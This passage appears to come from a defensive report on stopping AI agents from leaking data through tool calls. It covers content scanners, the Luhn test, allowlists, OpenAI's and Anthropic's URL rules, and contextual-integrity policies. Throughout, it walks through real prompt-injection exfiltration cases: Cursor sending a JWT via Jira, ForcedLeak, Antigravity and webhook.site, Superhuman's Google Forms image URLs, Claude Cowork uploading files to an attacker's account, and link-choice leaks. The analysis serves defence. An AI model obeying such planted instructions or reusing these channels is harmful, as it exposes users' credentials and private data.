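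Model Armor can either log a violation or log it and block the call. Google recommends starting with logging alone, to find out how often the filters would have blocked something. That mode is useless unless the customer turns on a separate logging service. Scanning can also spread the data it is meant to keep from leaving, because the log may contain snippets of the sensitive content and, in regions where Model Armor isn't available, Google may send the data to another jurisdiction for screening.

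### Patterns

Microsoft's *Learn about sensitive information types* lists three ways to identify sensitive items: manual labelling, automated pattern recognition and machine-learning classification. Pattern recognition is the simplest automatic method. A pattern describes the format of a value, such as three digits, a hyphen, two digits, a hyphen and four digits for a US social security number. Patterns can find almost anything with a fixed format, including bank account numbers, email addresses, database connection strings and many kinds of access key.

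Search patterns need little preparation because vendors supply large ready-made collections, though a company has to write its own for things like internal customer numbers. Their weakness is that they match any text in the right format, so a pattern for sixteen digits will match a parcel number or an order number as well as a card number.

### The Luhn checksum

Card numbers have a built-in test that removes most of these false matches. The last digit is a check digit, which the issuer calculates from the others using the Luhn algorithm. The University of New Brunswick's *Secrets of the LUHN-10 Algorithm* explains that the algorithm is meant to catch typing errors. To run the test, the scanner doubles every second digit, starting with the second from the right. If a doubled digit becomes a two-digit number, the scanner adds its two digits together. It then adds up all the results, including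 the digits it didn't double, and the number passes if the total is a multiple of 10.

The number in the ticket 4417 email, 4111 1111 1111 1111, is on PayPal's list of Visa test numbers. After the scanner removes the spaces, the sum works out like this:

```text
Digit        4  1  1  1    1  1  1  1    1  1  1  1    1  1  1  1
Multiply by  2  1  2  1    2  1  2  1    2  1  2  1    2  1  2  1
Result       8  1  2  1    2  1  2  1    2  1  2  1    2  1  2  1
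Group total      12             6             6             6

12 + 6 + 6 + 6 = 30
```

Since 30 is a multiple of 10, the number passes. If the last digit were 2, the total would be 31 and the number would fail.

About one random string of digits in ten also passes. For any first fifteen digits, exactly one choice of the sixteenth makes the total a multiple of 10, because the last digit is never doubled and changing it from 0 to 9 takes the total through ten consecutive values. If an agent's calls contained 1,000 random sixteen-digit order numbers, about 100 would look like valid card numbers.

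Some other numbers, including Canadian social insurance numbers and the IMEI numbers that identify mobile phones, always pass the checksum because their check digits are calculated the same way. An IMEI has fifteen digits, the same as an American Express card number, so a scanner that tested only length and checksum would flag every valid IMEI as a possible card number. It would have to check the opening digits or the surrounding words to tell them apart.

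Microsoft's commercial *Credit card number* detector combines these clues. It reports a low-confidence match when it finds 14 to 19 digits that match a major card brand and pass the Luhn test. A high-confidence match also requires an expiry date or a listed keyword within 300 characters. The keywords include "credit card" and "card number" but not "card" by itself. The ticket 4417 email has only "Card:" before the number, so a real card number in the same place would be a low-confidence match. "Reference number" is also a keyword, so a parcel reference that happened to fit a card format and pass the Luhn test could be a high-confidence match. An operator who acted only on high-confidence matches might therefore block the parcel reference and let the card number through.

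The Microsoft detector also deliberately ignores reserved test numbers, so testing a scanner with 4111 1111 1111 1111 may produce no alert even if the scanner is working properly.

### Registers of known values

An organisation that knows exactly which values it wants to protect can check each argument against a register of them. The register typically stores hashes, which are scrambled versions of the values that the software can compare but can't easily reverse. Unlike a pattern, a register can cover values with no fixed format, such as the home address in ticket 4417.

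Exact matching rarely mistakes one long number for another. If the register holds a million sixteen-digit card numbers, a random sixteen-digit string has about a one in ten billion chance of matching one of them. Short or common values produce more false matches, because a customer's surname may be an ordinary word and an age of 42 will match unrelated uses of that number. It therefore makes sense to require several values from the same record, such as a surname and a date of birth.

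This method takes far more preparation than pattern matching. Somebody has to extract the values, protect the register and update it as the database changes, or the scanner will miss the data of a customer who signed up this morning. The scanner also has to put values into a standard form before hashing them, because a card number with spaces has a different hash from the same number without them.

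### Document fingerprints

Fingerprinting applies a similar idea to whole documents. Typically, the software cuts a confidential document into overlapping runs of, say, eight words, hashes each run and stores some or all of the hashes. It does the same to the outgoing text and counts the matches. Changing one word affects at most eight runs, so a long extract with a few edits will still match.

Fingerprints match copied passages even if they contain no numbers or names. They can also match harmless text that many documents share, such as a standard confidentiality notice, unless somebody excludes it. The organisation has to choose which documents to register and re-register them whenever they change. A fingerprint of ticket 4417 would match the customer's complaint if the agent pasted it into the email. But the employee asked for a summary, which may not share any eight-word run with the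 original.

### Canaries

A canary is a made-up value planted among real data so that its appearance elsewhere indicates a leak. It might be a customer who doesn't exist or an access key that doesn't grant access to anything. A scanner only needs to search arguments for that exact value. False alarms should be rare because nobody has a legitimate reason to send it, although a backup job or a bulk export could cause one.

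Canaries are easy to prepare, but somebody has to plant them where a thief or a careless agent would pick them up, keep a list of them, and make sure staff don't treat them as real. Their main limitation is that they detect only leaks that include them. A planted record in the customer database can reveal that an agent is copying the whole table, but not that it has emailed one real customer's card number. Canaries are better suited to testing, including the exfiltration tests that NIST requires, because the tester knows what should not appear. Cartagena and Teixeira used planted data in this way in the GAP benchmark.

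### Trained classifiers

Much sensitive information has no fixed format and isn't listed in a register. A trained classifier is a machine-learning model that learns from examples labelled by people to estimate whether a text belongs to a category, such as medical notes, contracts or source code. It can recognise a new, unregistered document, and may still recognise one that has been reworded.

A classifier's errors are harder to predict than those of a pattern. A classifier for medical records may flag a public article about diabetes, and one for signed contracts may flag a blank one. Classifiers also need enough text to work with, and many arguments are only a few words long. To build a classifier, an organisation needs good examples of both the sensitive category and harmless material that resembles it. It must then choose the score that triggers an alert. A lower threshold finds more leaks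 but produces more false alarms.

### Aegis

*AEGIS* (Yuan, Su and Zhao, 2026) describes an open-source program that scans arguments before the tool runs. Its client modifies the software libraries an agent uses to call its model. When the model's response contains a tool call, the client suspends execution and sends the tool's name and arguments to a separate gateway for a decision.

The Aegis gateway first extracts the text from a call's arguments, including text in nested lists and objects that a scanner reading only the top levels would miss. It goes down 32 levels and collects up to 10,000 pieces of text. If it reaches either limit, it marks the call as suspicious. It then compares the text with 22 detection patterns and checks the call against the operator's policies.

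Aegis allows low-risk and medium-risk calls, blocks calls that violate a policy, and holds other high-risk calls as "pending" until a person approves or rejects them.

Twenty of the 22 patterns have little to do with DLP. They look for things such as database attacks, dangerous shell commands, injected instructions and paths to sensitive files. Of the other two, one looks for 11 types of personal data and credentials, and the other flags more than 5 kilobytes of data in a call with an external web address. The ticket 4417 email is far too short for the size rule, so catching it would depend on the personal-data pattern.

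Yuan and colleagues give a similar example, an email with a social security number and a card number in the body. They label it as allowed, but the response they print is "pending", with high risk. The response also lists an email address among the personal data. The only email address in the call is the recipient's, so any normal email would produce at least one such match. Combining all the text is a good way to find hidden values, but a scanner also has to track which field each value came from.

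The tests were encouraging but say little about data leaks. Aegis blocked all 48 attacks in a set that Yuan and colleagues put together from known techniques:

| Type of attack | Blocked |
|---|---|
| Database (SQL) injection | 11 of 11 |
| Prompt injection | 11 of 11 |
| Shell commands | 8 of 8 |
| Path traversal (reaching files outside the permitted folder) | 7 of 7 |
| Sensitive files | 6 of 6 |
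| Deeply nested text | 3 of 3 |
| Data exfiltration | 2 of 2 |

Only two of the attacks were exfiltration, and none was in the personal-data category. Both exfiltration attacks were detected, but even if they had been a random sample of real attempts, that result would be compatible with a true detection rate as low as 22% (at 95% confidence). Both also used known techniques, and Yuan and colleagues acknowledge that the patterns may miss new ones.

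Aegis raised six false alarms on 500 harmless calls (1.2%), all on database queries with "or" in their conditions. The calls included database queries, file reads, API requests and text processing. The rate could be very different for an agent that sends customer emails all day, especially since the card pattern printed in the appendix matches any 13 to 16 digits without a Luhn test, including the 13-digit timestamps that many programs use.

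Scanning seems fast enough to be practical. Across 1,000 calls on a local installation, Aegis added a median of 8.3 milliseconds and at most 23.1 milliseconds for 99% of calls, while a model commonly takes between one and thirty seconds to respond. However, Aegis can't inspect anything that bypasses its client. For example, it would scan a command that starts a script, but not the web requests the script itself makes.

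### The Cursor and Jira case

Zenity Labs' *AgentFlayer* (August 2025) describes a harder test for content scanning, because the attacker disguised what the agent was looking for. It gives the full account of the demonstration in which a ticket told a coding agent to send off a credential and mention only a timeout. The agent was Cursor, an AI code editor, connected through MCP to Jira, which tracks software tasks. Many companies automatically copy customer support requests into Jira, so an outsider can get text into a ticket by sending an email.

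In the first Jira ticket, the researcher asked for API keys, and Cursor refused on security grounds. The researcher then replaced the term with the name of a fruit and described what the value looked like. Cursor searched the code repository, found a JSON Web Token (JWT), a credential software uses to authenticate itself, and sent it out. Zenity Labs describes sending the token either in a comment on the ticket or in the address of a web request.

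A scan of the ticket for words such as "password" or "API key" would have found nothing, because the instructions used a new name for the token. The token itself kept its normal format, and Willison (2025) points out that the characters "eyJ" at its start identify it as a JWT. A JWT is made of encoded blocks separated by dots. The first block encodes structured data that opens with a brace and a quotation mark, which this encoding always turns into "eyJ". The JWT pattern in Aegis includes this opening and the dots, so it would very likely have matched the token in either the comment or the web address. The scanner wouldn't have needed to decode the address, because a JWT contains only characters that web addresses leave unchanged.

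Other scanners would have missed the JWT. JWTs are not among Google's six basic data types, and a single one is normally far too small to trigger the Aegis size rule. A register would have caught the token only if somebody had already entered it.

In a second test, the ticket led Cursor to dummy Amazon cloud credentials in a file outside the repository. Cursor rejected several versions before one worked. As in the first test, the researcher had encoded the instructions, so a filter on incoming text would have had to decode them first. Cursor prepared a web request containing the credentials, but the request did not run because the researcher had turned off automatic execution as a precaution.

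Amazon's credentials have two parts. The key's identifier has a recognisable opening, but the secret part is a random string that is hard to identify without its context. A scan could also have stopped this attempt earlier, before the agent read the credentials, if the agent supplied the file's path as an argument. The ticket was worded to avoid naming the file, but a tool needs the path to open it, and the folder for Amazon credentials is on the Aegis list of sensitive locations.

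A format match would not have been enough to decide whether to block the call, because developers legitimately send JWTs to their own servers when they test a login. The destination matters too. But a destination check would probably have trusted the Jira comment, since it would have gone to the company's own system, and some companies copy Jira comments back to the customer who sent the email. For the Jira comment, the content was a better clue than the destination.

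Cursor replied that this was a known issue and recommended that users connect only to MCP servers with trusted content and exclude sensitive files from the agent's access. Zenity Labs considers such exclusions a best-effort measure.

### What removes the match

The Cursor attack left the token unchanged. Content matching is much less reliable when data changes form before the agent sends it, which can happen even without an attacker.

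Summaries, paraphrases and translations mostly affect information expressed in words. A card number stays the same in a French summary of an English document, but the wording of a diagnosis or a plan to buy another company changes. Patterns, registers and fingerprints can miss the reworded version, though a classifier might recognise it. In the experiment by Dong and colleagues, the protected details included a customer's age and income, which can appear in an ordinary sentence, so a format scan would have had little to match.

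Encoding rewrites data in other characters by a public rule, so a scanner can reverse it if it tries the right rule. Each extra attempt takes time and can produce new false matches, and some products don't try. Model Armor, for example, does not decode Base64, hexadecimal or URL encoding, three of the most common forms. Encrypted data is harder to scan because reversing it requires the key. A scanner could flag text that looks random, but many legitimate arguments also look random, including the opaque identifiers that MCP recommends.

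Sometimes the sensitive data is not in the argument. In the Copilot Cowork case, the message contained download links to the user's files, so a scan for card numbers would have found none even if the files contained them. Model Armor also checks each item separately, so data spread over several calls can get through in pieces.

Harmful commands are a separate problem because they may contain nothing sensitive, as with the deleted drive. Patterns for dangerous commands help to some extent, and Aegis holds a command that deletes a running server component until a person approves it. But matching a pattern does not show whether a deletion is the right one. Yuan and colleagues' sample policy for keeping a database read-only rejects any query containing words such as "DELETE" or "CREATE" in capitals. It would block a harmless query for a column called "CREATED_AT" and, as printed, would allow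 "delete" and "create" commands in lower case, which databases treat identically.

### Accidental leaks

A determined attacker can exploit these limits to get past a filter, which supports Willison's distrust of filters. Filters work better against accidental leaks. An overzealous agent that copies a card number into an email has no reason to encode it, so a pattern with a Luhn test will usually find it.

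There is fairly good evidence that agents often make this kind of mistake, at least in tests. Even in the AgentLeak scenarios without attacks, nearly half of the unfiltered final answers contained unnecessary private data, and every model tested put such data into tool inputs in most scenarios. The GPT-5.2 runs that masked social security numbers only in the text show that models sometimes pass on such numbers in their original format, though these weren't accidents in the same sense.

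It is less clear how many accidental leaks a content scan would catch. AgentLeak defines a leak broadly, so simple matching would probably have found only some of the leaks it counted, and its figures don't measure how often real deployments send card numbers or credentials to the wrong place. Still, scanning for card numbers and credentials takes a few milliseconds per call, and a leaked card number or password can do a lot of damage. That seems enough to justify the scan, provided the operator doesn't take a clean result as proof that a call is safe.

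## Checking where the data is going

The outside address in the copy field would be suspicious even if a scanner found nothing sensitive in the ticket 4417 email. A destination check compares the recipient or web address in a call with the places where the agent may send things. It doesn't have to recognise the data, so it still works when the agent has reworded, translated or encrypted what it sends. Its main weakness is that it usually relies on the domain in an address, which often reveals little about who will end up with the data. In four cases that researchers disclosed between September 2025 and January 2026, private data could leave through a domain that the vendor had approved.

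### Domains, addresses, accounts and readers

The destination of a call is everyone who can read the data once the tool has run. The arguments don't list these readers, so a check has to infer them from the domain, the full address and the account behind the address.

| | Ticket 4417 email | Web request | Where a check can find it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Domain | `outside.example` | `docs.google.com` | In the argument |
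| Full address | `archive@outside.example` | The whole web address, including any data added at the end | In the argument |
| Account | Whoever holds that mailbox | The owner of the form or folder at that address, or of the key sent with the request | Sometimes in the argument, often only in the service's own records |
| Reader | Everyone who can open the mailbox or receives mail forwarded from it | Everyone with access to that account or to the website's logs | Usually nowhere that the agent's operator can look |

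On a large service, millions of unrelated people hold accounts under one domain. An address inside the employee's own company may be a mailing list with outside members. Conversely, an outside address such as `archive@outside.example` might belong to a supplier that the company pays to archive its email, but only somebody who knew about the contract could tell.

### Egress filtering and allowlists

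Egress filtering means monitoring outgoing network traffic and blocking some of it. A strict filter allows connections only to a list of permitted destinations, called an allowlist. A looser filter blocks only known bad destinations, so it doesn't stop traffic to a domain an attacker has just registered. The payment card industry's security standard requires companies to restrict outgoing traffic from systems that handle card data, so many companies already do some egress filtering.

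A network filter would not stop the ticket 4417 email, because the email travels over an encrypted connection to the company's usual mail service. The allowlist therefore has to apply to the arguments. A rule that `send_email` can send only to addresses at `company.example` would block the copy to `archive@outside.example` without checking the body.

Even a rule this simple is easy to get wrong. It must check every field that can hold a recipient, including each entry in a list and any blind-copy field. It must also compare whole domain names, because a search for "company.example" would accept `notcompany.example`, which could belong to a stranger. Data can also go to the addresses of links and images in the body, as the Copilot Cowork messages to the user's own account showed.

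The rule would also offer little protection if the agent writes to customers. Many customers have addresses at the big public mail providers, so the list would have to permit those domains, and an attacker can open a mailbox at one of them in a minute. The operator would have to list individual addresses instead, such as the one in each customer's record.

Where a short list of allowed destinations is practical, it can stop leaks that other checks would probably miss. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* describes an internal exercise from February 2026 in which a researcher tricked a colleague into pasting a prompt into Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent. Among ordinary setup steps, the prompt asked the agent to encode the colleague's cloud credentials and send them to an outside address. Claude did so in 24 of 25 repetitions. Because the request came from the user, comparing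 the call with the user's instructions would have revealed no conflict, and a simple content scan would have missed the encoded credentials. Anthropic concludes that only limits on where the agent can connect and which files it can open would have stopped the leak.

For command-line tools, it makes more sense to apply the list to network connections than to arguments, because the address may be inside a script that the command starts. Claude Code has a sandbox, a restricted environment for running commands, that denies network access by default. This kind of filter covers the script's own web requests, which Aegis cannot inspect, but it misses any traffic that doesn't pass through it. Cloud Security Alliance's *Top 6 Claude Cowork Security Risks to Watch* warns that web search and web fetch in Anthropic's desktop agent entirely bypass the agent's controls on outbound traffic. An operator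 relying on the network list would need a separate rule for the arguments of those two tools.

Records of outgoing traffic are also good evidence after the fact. In the local test setup of *Silent Egress* (2026), malicious web pages got an agent to make unintended requests about 89% of the time. Checks on the agent's answers missed 95% of the successful attacks, while traffic monitoring raised no false alarms in the control runs. It would probably raise some for an agent that browses all day, since that agent keeps contacting new sites for legitimate reasons.

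### Four leaks through approved domains

ForcedLeak, which the security company Noma disclosed in September 2025, depended on who owned a domain. It affected Agentforce, Salesforce's platform for business agents. An outsider could hide instructions in a company's online sales enquiry form. When an employee asked the agent about that enquiry, the agent wrote an image address containing the email addresses of the company's sales leads. The employee's browser then fetched it, much as in EchoLeak.

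This address passed the app's content security policy (CSP), a list of the sites from which a web app allows the browser to load material. Salesforce's list included `my-salesforce-cms.com`, but the domain's registration had expired, so Noma's researchers were able to buy it. Noma told Salesforce Ben, a news site for Salesforce users, that the theft "would have been impossible" without a way around the policy. According to The Hacker News' *Salesforce Patches Critical ForcedLeak* (2025), Salesforce took back the domain and stopped its agents from sending output to untrusted addresses. The entry was presumably correct when somebody added it, so an allowlist needs regular checks that each domain still has the same owner.

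PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data* describes an attack on Antigravity, Google's AI code editor. A web page with hidden instructions got the agent to collect cloud credentials and pieces of code, put them into a `webhook.site` address, and pass that address to its browser tool. The tool's allowlist included `webhook.site` by default. The domain had the right owner, but it should never have been on the list, because anyone can create an address there and read every request sent to it. This is useful for testing software, but it also lets an attacker receive stolen data.

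PromptArmor published the flaw without first reporting it privately, because Google had already indicated that it knew about such risks. Willison (2025) noted that Google listed data exfiltration through the browser agent as a known issue that it was working to fix. Neither PromptArmor nor Willison reported that the entry was removed. Removing it would not have stopped every leak, since PromptArmor found three others that didn't need the browser tool. *Faking the Pipeline* (Odson and Morris, June 2026) reported another leak from Antigravity that used its ability to display images in the chat.

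The Superhuman case is harder to blame on a careless list, because the approved domain was `docs.google.com`. The email app's CSP allowed images from that domain, which also hosts Google Forms. A form's creator can make links with the answers already filled in, and opening such a link can submit the form. In PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails*, a user asked for a summary of recent mail, which included an email with planted instructions. Those instructions made the assistant write an image address that linked to the attacker's form, with the contents of other emails filled in as answers. The browser submitted the form when it tried to load the image. A single answer could leak the full text of several emails, or parts of more than 40.

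A domain check could not have caught this, because the attacker's form and the company's own documents are on the same domain. The full address would have revealed more, since it identified a form and contained the text of private emails. PromptArmor reported the problem on the night of Friday, 5 December 2025. Superhuman disabled the affected features that Monday, released a first patch the next day, and released more before both companies agreed to publication on 12 January 2026.

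An attack on Claude Cowork, Anthropic's desktop agent for office work (not Microsoft's Copilot Cowork), sent a user's file out through Anthropic's own domain. Cowork's web tools bypass its egress controls, but it runs code in a virtual machine, a simulated computer that can connect to only a few domains. One of them is `api.anthropic.com`, because Cowork can't work without Anthropic's service. PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files*, published two days after a preview version launched in January 2026, describes how a document with hidden instructions made the agent upload a file of loan details to Anthropic's file storage. The upload command included the attacker's API key, a credential that tells the service whose account to use, so the file appeared in the attacker's account.

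The egress filter let the upload through because the domain was on its list of allowed domains. The full address would also have looked normal, because every customer uploads files to the same one, and only the account was wrong. A scan of the argument for social security numbers would have found none, because a command of this kind names the file without containing its text. A scan for credentials might have flagged the attacker's key, although developers often put keys in commands.

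Anthropic's fix checks which account a request uses. A proxy, a program that relays network traffic, now runs inside the virtual machine and passes requests to Anthropic's service only if they carry the token that Cowork issued to that machine for that session. The check has to be on the user's side because Anthropic's servers can't distinguish a Cowork request from any other customer's. Anthropic could have fixed the problem sooner. *Claude Pirate*, a post on Johann Rehberger's security blog Embrace The Red, described the same upload route in Claude's chat product in October 2025, before Cowork existed. PromptArmor notes that Anthropic acknowledged that flaw without fixing it.

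Anthropic now thinks of an allowlist entry as a "capability grant". By approving a domain, an operator gives the agent, and anyone who gains control of it, every function available there. This view seems to fit all of these cases except ForcedLeak, where the domain had changed owners. On this view, large, reputable services are also riskier to allowlist than they look, because they offer so many functions to so many account holders.

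That lesson has been slow to spread. Another Salesforce product, Agentforce Coworker, removes web addresses by default, and administrators list the exceptions. Salesforce's *Add Trusted URLs for Agentforce Coworker (Beta)* gives `docs.google.com`, the domain in the Superhuman attack, as an example of an address to add. Whether this is dangerous depends on the other settings. PromptArmor's *One Key Way Salesforce Mitigates AI Risk* recommends blocking images from listed sites unless the company needs them, and avoiding broad entries that cover any site where outsiders can post content.

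An account check like Anthropic's works well when there is only one legitimate account. It would be much harder to apply to Google's documents, where staff may have good reasons to open files belonging to hundreds of people.

### OpenAI's public-address rule

In January 2026, OpenAI explained the rule behind ChatGPT's Safe Url check, which it uses instead of relying on a list of trusted sites. An agent may automatically fetch a web address only if an independent crawler has already recorded that exact address. A crawler is a program that finds and records public web pages, as search engines do. OpenAI's crawler has no access to conversations or accounts, so an address in its index is unlikely to contain one user's private data. If the agent tried to open an address ending in the card number from ticket 4417, the address would fail the check whatever its domain, because the crawler would never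 have recorded it.

If an address isn't in the index, either the agent has to try another website or the user has to approve the visit. Users who see many warnings may stop reading them.

OpenAI rejected a site list for two reasons. A strict list would raise too many false alarms, since people visit many sites beyond the well-known ones. A list can also be bypassed through a redirect, which is a reply from a website that sends the browser to a different address. Many respectable sites use redirects, for example to count clicks. The tool call contains only the first address, so a check on the argument can approve a trusted domain that then redirects the browser to an untrusted one.

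The security company Tenable found such a hole in an earlier version of ChatGPT's link check, which always allowed addresses at `bing.com`. Bing wraps its search results in `bing.com` links that forward to the sites it has found. Tenable's researchers had their own sites in Bing's results, so they could get ChatGPT to open those sites through links that the check approved. A domain list would catch this only if the tool itself checked every address in the chain of redirects, because the later ones never appear in an argument.

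Exact matching mostly prevents redirects from leaking a user's data. A redirect can normally pass on the data only if the data is in the first address, and an address containing it would not be in the index.

OpenAI published the paper *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents* along with the rule. According to Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, the paper acknowledges that some leakage remains possible. An attacker may own many pages already in the index, and the agent's choice of which ones to open can carry information. Rehberger had described this possibility in 2023. The blog calls the rule a significant improvement but not a complete solution.

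OpenAI promises only that the agent won't quietly leak a user's data in the address when it fetches something. The rule would have blocked the ForcedLeak, Antigravity and Superhuman addresses, which all contained private data. It does not make a page's content trustworthy or keep planted instructions away from the model. It also does little about uploads, and would probably not have stopped the one in the Claude Cowork case, because the address was the same for every customer and the private file was in the body of the request.

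A rule also protects only the products that apply it. Embrace The Red points out that an earlier version of the check was missing from ChatGPT's macOS and iOS apps, and that some OpenAI developers may not know to use the new one. Three months after OpenAI's announcement, PromptArmor's *Codex for Everything Exfiltrates Connected Data* reported the Google Forms leak again, this time in OpenAI's agent Codex. The address contained the user's emails, so it can't have been in the crawler's index, and presumably Codex was not running the check on images. OpenAI has since fixed the flaw.

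### The web_fetch rule and its gap

Anthropic had introduced a related rule in September 2025 with `web_fetch`, a tool that lets Claude read web pages. Claude can fetch only addresses that have already appeared in the conversation, not ones it composes itself. In Willison's account of the original documentation, these addresses could come from the user's messages, results from the developer's own tools, or earlier web searches and fetches.

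Willison warned that developers often paste untrusted material, such as emails, into what the software treats as the user's message, so an attacker's link could count as permitted. But the attacker would have to write the whole address before knowing any of the user's data, and Claude could not add anything to it, so a theft that depended on attaching private data to a link would fail.

In July 2026, a researcher, Ayush Paul, disclosed a gap in the rule. Claude could follow links on pages it had already fetched, so a website could offer it a set of links to choose from. The rule permitted every link and Claude had written none of them, but the sequence it followed revealed the user's name, employer and home city to the site's owner. Willison (2026), who had admired the tool's design, called this a hole in it.

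Anthropic closed the gap by stopping `web_fetch` from following links that it finds in fetched pages. It paid Paul no bounty, saying it had already found the problem internally. Claude can no longer use the tool to go from one page to the next as a human reader would. In *The Read-Only Lie*, the pseudonymous blogger dyb argues that Anthropic closed this channel but left the condition that created it, because even a read-only tool sends information out in its requests. That seems right, since Claude can still choose among search results, although an attacker would need several of their own pages in those results to learn much from the choice.

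### How much a permitted choice can carry

Computer scientists have worked on this problem for over fifty years. In *A Note on the Confinement Problem* (1973), Butler Lampson considered a customer who runs somebody else's program on private data and wants to be sure it can't pass the data to its owner. Lampson called this confinement. Some of the channels he described are obvious, such as a file that the owner can read later. Others are covert, meaning that nobody intended them for communication, such as the program's effect on how busy the computer is. Between these are legitimate outputs with a hidden use. A program that has to send its owner a bill, for example, can choose an amount that also encodes some of the customer's data. The links in the July 2026 case resemble the bill, because each was a legitimate request but the choice of links carried the information.

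The number of values an argument can take limits how much it can leak. If n values are permitted, an observer who sees the chosen value can distinguish at most n messages, so one call carries at most log₂(n) bits, where a bit is the information in the answer to one yes-or-no question. A choice between two links carries at most one bit, and a choice among eight carries at most three. The limit is zero only when n is 1, and even then the observer may learn something from whether the agent made the call.

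The limits add up over several calls, so k calls with n choices each carry at most k × log₂(n) bits. A sixteen-digit card number has fifteen free digits, because the Luhn algorithm determines the last one from the others. That makes 10¹⁵ possibilities, or about 49.8 bits. The table shows the minimum number of calls needed to transmit any such number through the choice of value alone.

| Permitted values | Most bits per call | Fewest calls for a card number |
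|---|---|---|
| 1 | 0 | Impossible |
| 2 | 1 | 50 |
| 36 | 5.2 | 10 |
| 1,000 | 10.0 | 5 |
| 1,000,000 | 19.9 | 3 |

For OpenAI's rule, n is normally the number of indexed pages an attacker can monitor, not the size of the whole index, because the attacker doesn't learn about visits to other pages. But Embrace The Red notes that a larger blog probably already has 36 pages in the index, enough for one per letter and digit, and that an attacker could prepare thousands.

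A leak would usually carry less data than the limit, because reaching it requires the model to make every choice as the attacker wants. *Silent Egress* tested a different way of spreading data over several requests, and one of its measures of leakage was 73% lower than when everything was sent at once.

Embrace The Red suggests preventing an agent from opening the same address twice in a session. This would disrupt simple schemes that need to repeat a letter, but it hardly changes the theoretical limit on how much data can leak. With 36 addresses and ten visits, the limit falls from 51.7 bits to 49.7. If the attacker also couldn't tell the order of the visits, it would fall to 27.9 bits. Capping the number of fetches, which Anthropic lets developers do, makes a bigger difference. With 36 addresses and a cap of five, the limit is about 26 bits, which is enough to pick out one person among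 60 million but far too little for a card number.

Kevin Borders and Atul Prakash applied this reasoning to network monitoring in *Quantifying Information Leaks in Outbound Web Traffic* (2009). They argued that content scanners can't recognise encrypted or disguised data, so a monitor should instead measure the most information outgoing traffic could carry. Most of a web request repeats earlier requests or follows from the page the user was on, so a monitor with access to both can subtract the predictable part. On real browsing traffic, their method discounted 98.5% of the bytes.

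The same subtraction explains why the OpenAI and Anthropic rules help. An 80-character web address normally takes 640 bits to store. If Claude copied it from a list of ten search results, the choice carries at most 3.3 bits of information. If Claude composed the address itself, most of it could be private data. Both companies let the agent select an address freely but stop it from writing a new one without involving the user.

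An allowlist for email recipients limits who receives a message but not how much it can contain. The body is free text, and 100 ordinary keyboard characters can hold over 650 bits. If `archive@outside.example` were removed from the recipients of the ticket 4417 email, the email would pass any sensible destination check, but the account manager would still receive the customer's full card number.

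## Whether this recipient may have this data for this task

The ticket 4417 email shouldn't contain the customer's card number, even if it goes only to the account manager. A content scan can find the number and a destination check can confirm who gets the email, but deciding whether this colleague may have this number for this task requires a rule that covers the recipient, the data and the task together. Companies can write such rules for narrow tasks and structured fields. Writing them for free text and vague requests, which people often give agents, is much harder.

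### Three permissions

To send the summary, the support agent needs permission to read the ticket, permission to use `send_email`, and permission to put the ticket's contents into that email. Many systems control only the first two, so an agent allowed to read a record and send email can send the whole record.

Dong and colleagues describe a gap between access and authorisation. Ordinary tool permissions determine whether an agent may call a tool, but not which values it may put into each argument, for what purpose or for whom. For example, a company might let an agent use a customer's occupation to route a support request but not let it send the occupation to a marketing service.

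Taking away the agent's access to the data would solve this problem, but the agent often needs the data to do its task. If the agent also arranges replacement deliveries, it needs the customer's home address for the courier, and the address then stays in its context when it writes the next email.

### Contextual integrity

The philosopher Helen Nissenbaum (2004), in *Privacy as Contextual Integrity*, proposed a theory of privacy that fits this problem well. Its central idea is that sharing personal information violates privacy only when it breaks the norms of its setting, as when a priest repeats a confession. *The danger of contextual integrity* describes this as perhaps the dominant theory of privacy now among policy-oriented scholars in law and computer science.

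*Contextual Integrity Up and Down the Data Food Chain* (Nissenbaum, 2019) describes such norms with five parameters: the subject, the sender, the recipient, the type of information and the "transmission principle". The transmission principle is the condition on which the information passes, such as consent, confidentiality or a legal duty. Judging a case requires all five, because people fill in a missing one differently and then disagree.

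Suppose the agent had also copied the customer's home address into the body of the email for ticket 4417. The table applies the five parameters to that flow.

| Parameter | In the ticket 4417 email | A change that could alter the judgement |
|---|---|---|
| Subject | The customer | The address is the account manager's own |
| Sender | The support agent, acting for an employee | The customer writes to the account manager directly |
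| Recipient | The account manager | A courier, or the outside archive |
| Type of information | A home address | Only the customer's city |
| Transmission principle | The customer gave it to get a complaint resolved | The customer agreed to a home visit |

The address is a borderline case. In many companies an account manager can look up a customer's address anyway, and the customer might not mind. The outside archive is harder to justify unless the customer accepted terms that cover it.

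The five parameters don't include the purpose of the email, which matters here because the same account manager might need the address tomorrow to plan a visit. US health and financial privacy rules often mention use, and Nissenbaum was "increasingly persuaded" by a colleague's proposal to add it as a parameter.

Contextual integrity also differs from data minimisation, the principle of sharing only what a task needs. Nissenbaum rejects the idea that privacy means minimisation. Under a minimisation test, the home address clearly doesn't belong in the email, because a summary of a double charge makes sense without it. Researchers who build checks for agents mostly apply this stricter test or combine the two, so they count more violations than they would using contextual integrity alone.

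### A violation test for one value

Dong and colleagues turn these ideas into a test that a program can apply to each value in a proposed call:

```text
A value d in field f is a violation if
    d was available in the model's context, and
    f contains d, or something derived from d, and
    the policy does not allow this combination of
        source, datum, purpose, recipient and field
```

The test includes the field because a value may belong in one of a tool's fields but not another. A courier tool might need the home address in `ship_to` but not in a free-text `notes` field that is printed on the label.

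Checking the first two conditions mostly means searching text. The third is harder to check because someone must already have decided which combinations of recipient, data and task the policy allows.

### The Claw in Plain Sight experiment

Dong and colleagues applied this test in their product-offer experiment. In the attack, which they call Claw in Plain Sight, an untrusted memo claimed that the task required an invented customer's protected details: age, gender, income bracket and occupation.

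The experiment varied the memo's pressure over six levels. At the lowest level there was no memo, only empty slots for the profile. At the highest, a supposed compliance lead ordered the model to fill in the fields regardless of its other instructions. The policy varied over four levels, from no visible rule to one that prohibited sending the protected details to this destination for this purpose and took precedence over any memo. Five models each went through all 24 combinations once, for a total of 120 sessions. A session counted as a leak if the proposed arguments contained an exact copy of at least one protected detail.

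The table gives the number of leaks in the six sessions that each model had under each policy.

| Model | No visible rule | General rule to minimise data | Named fields prohibited | Prohibition tied to purpose and destination |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| DeepSeek-V4-Flash | 6 | 5 | 4 | 0 |
| DeepSeek-V4-Pro | 6 | 4 | 1 | 0 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 4 | 5 | 5 | 4 |
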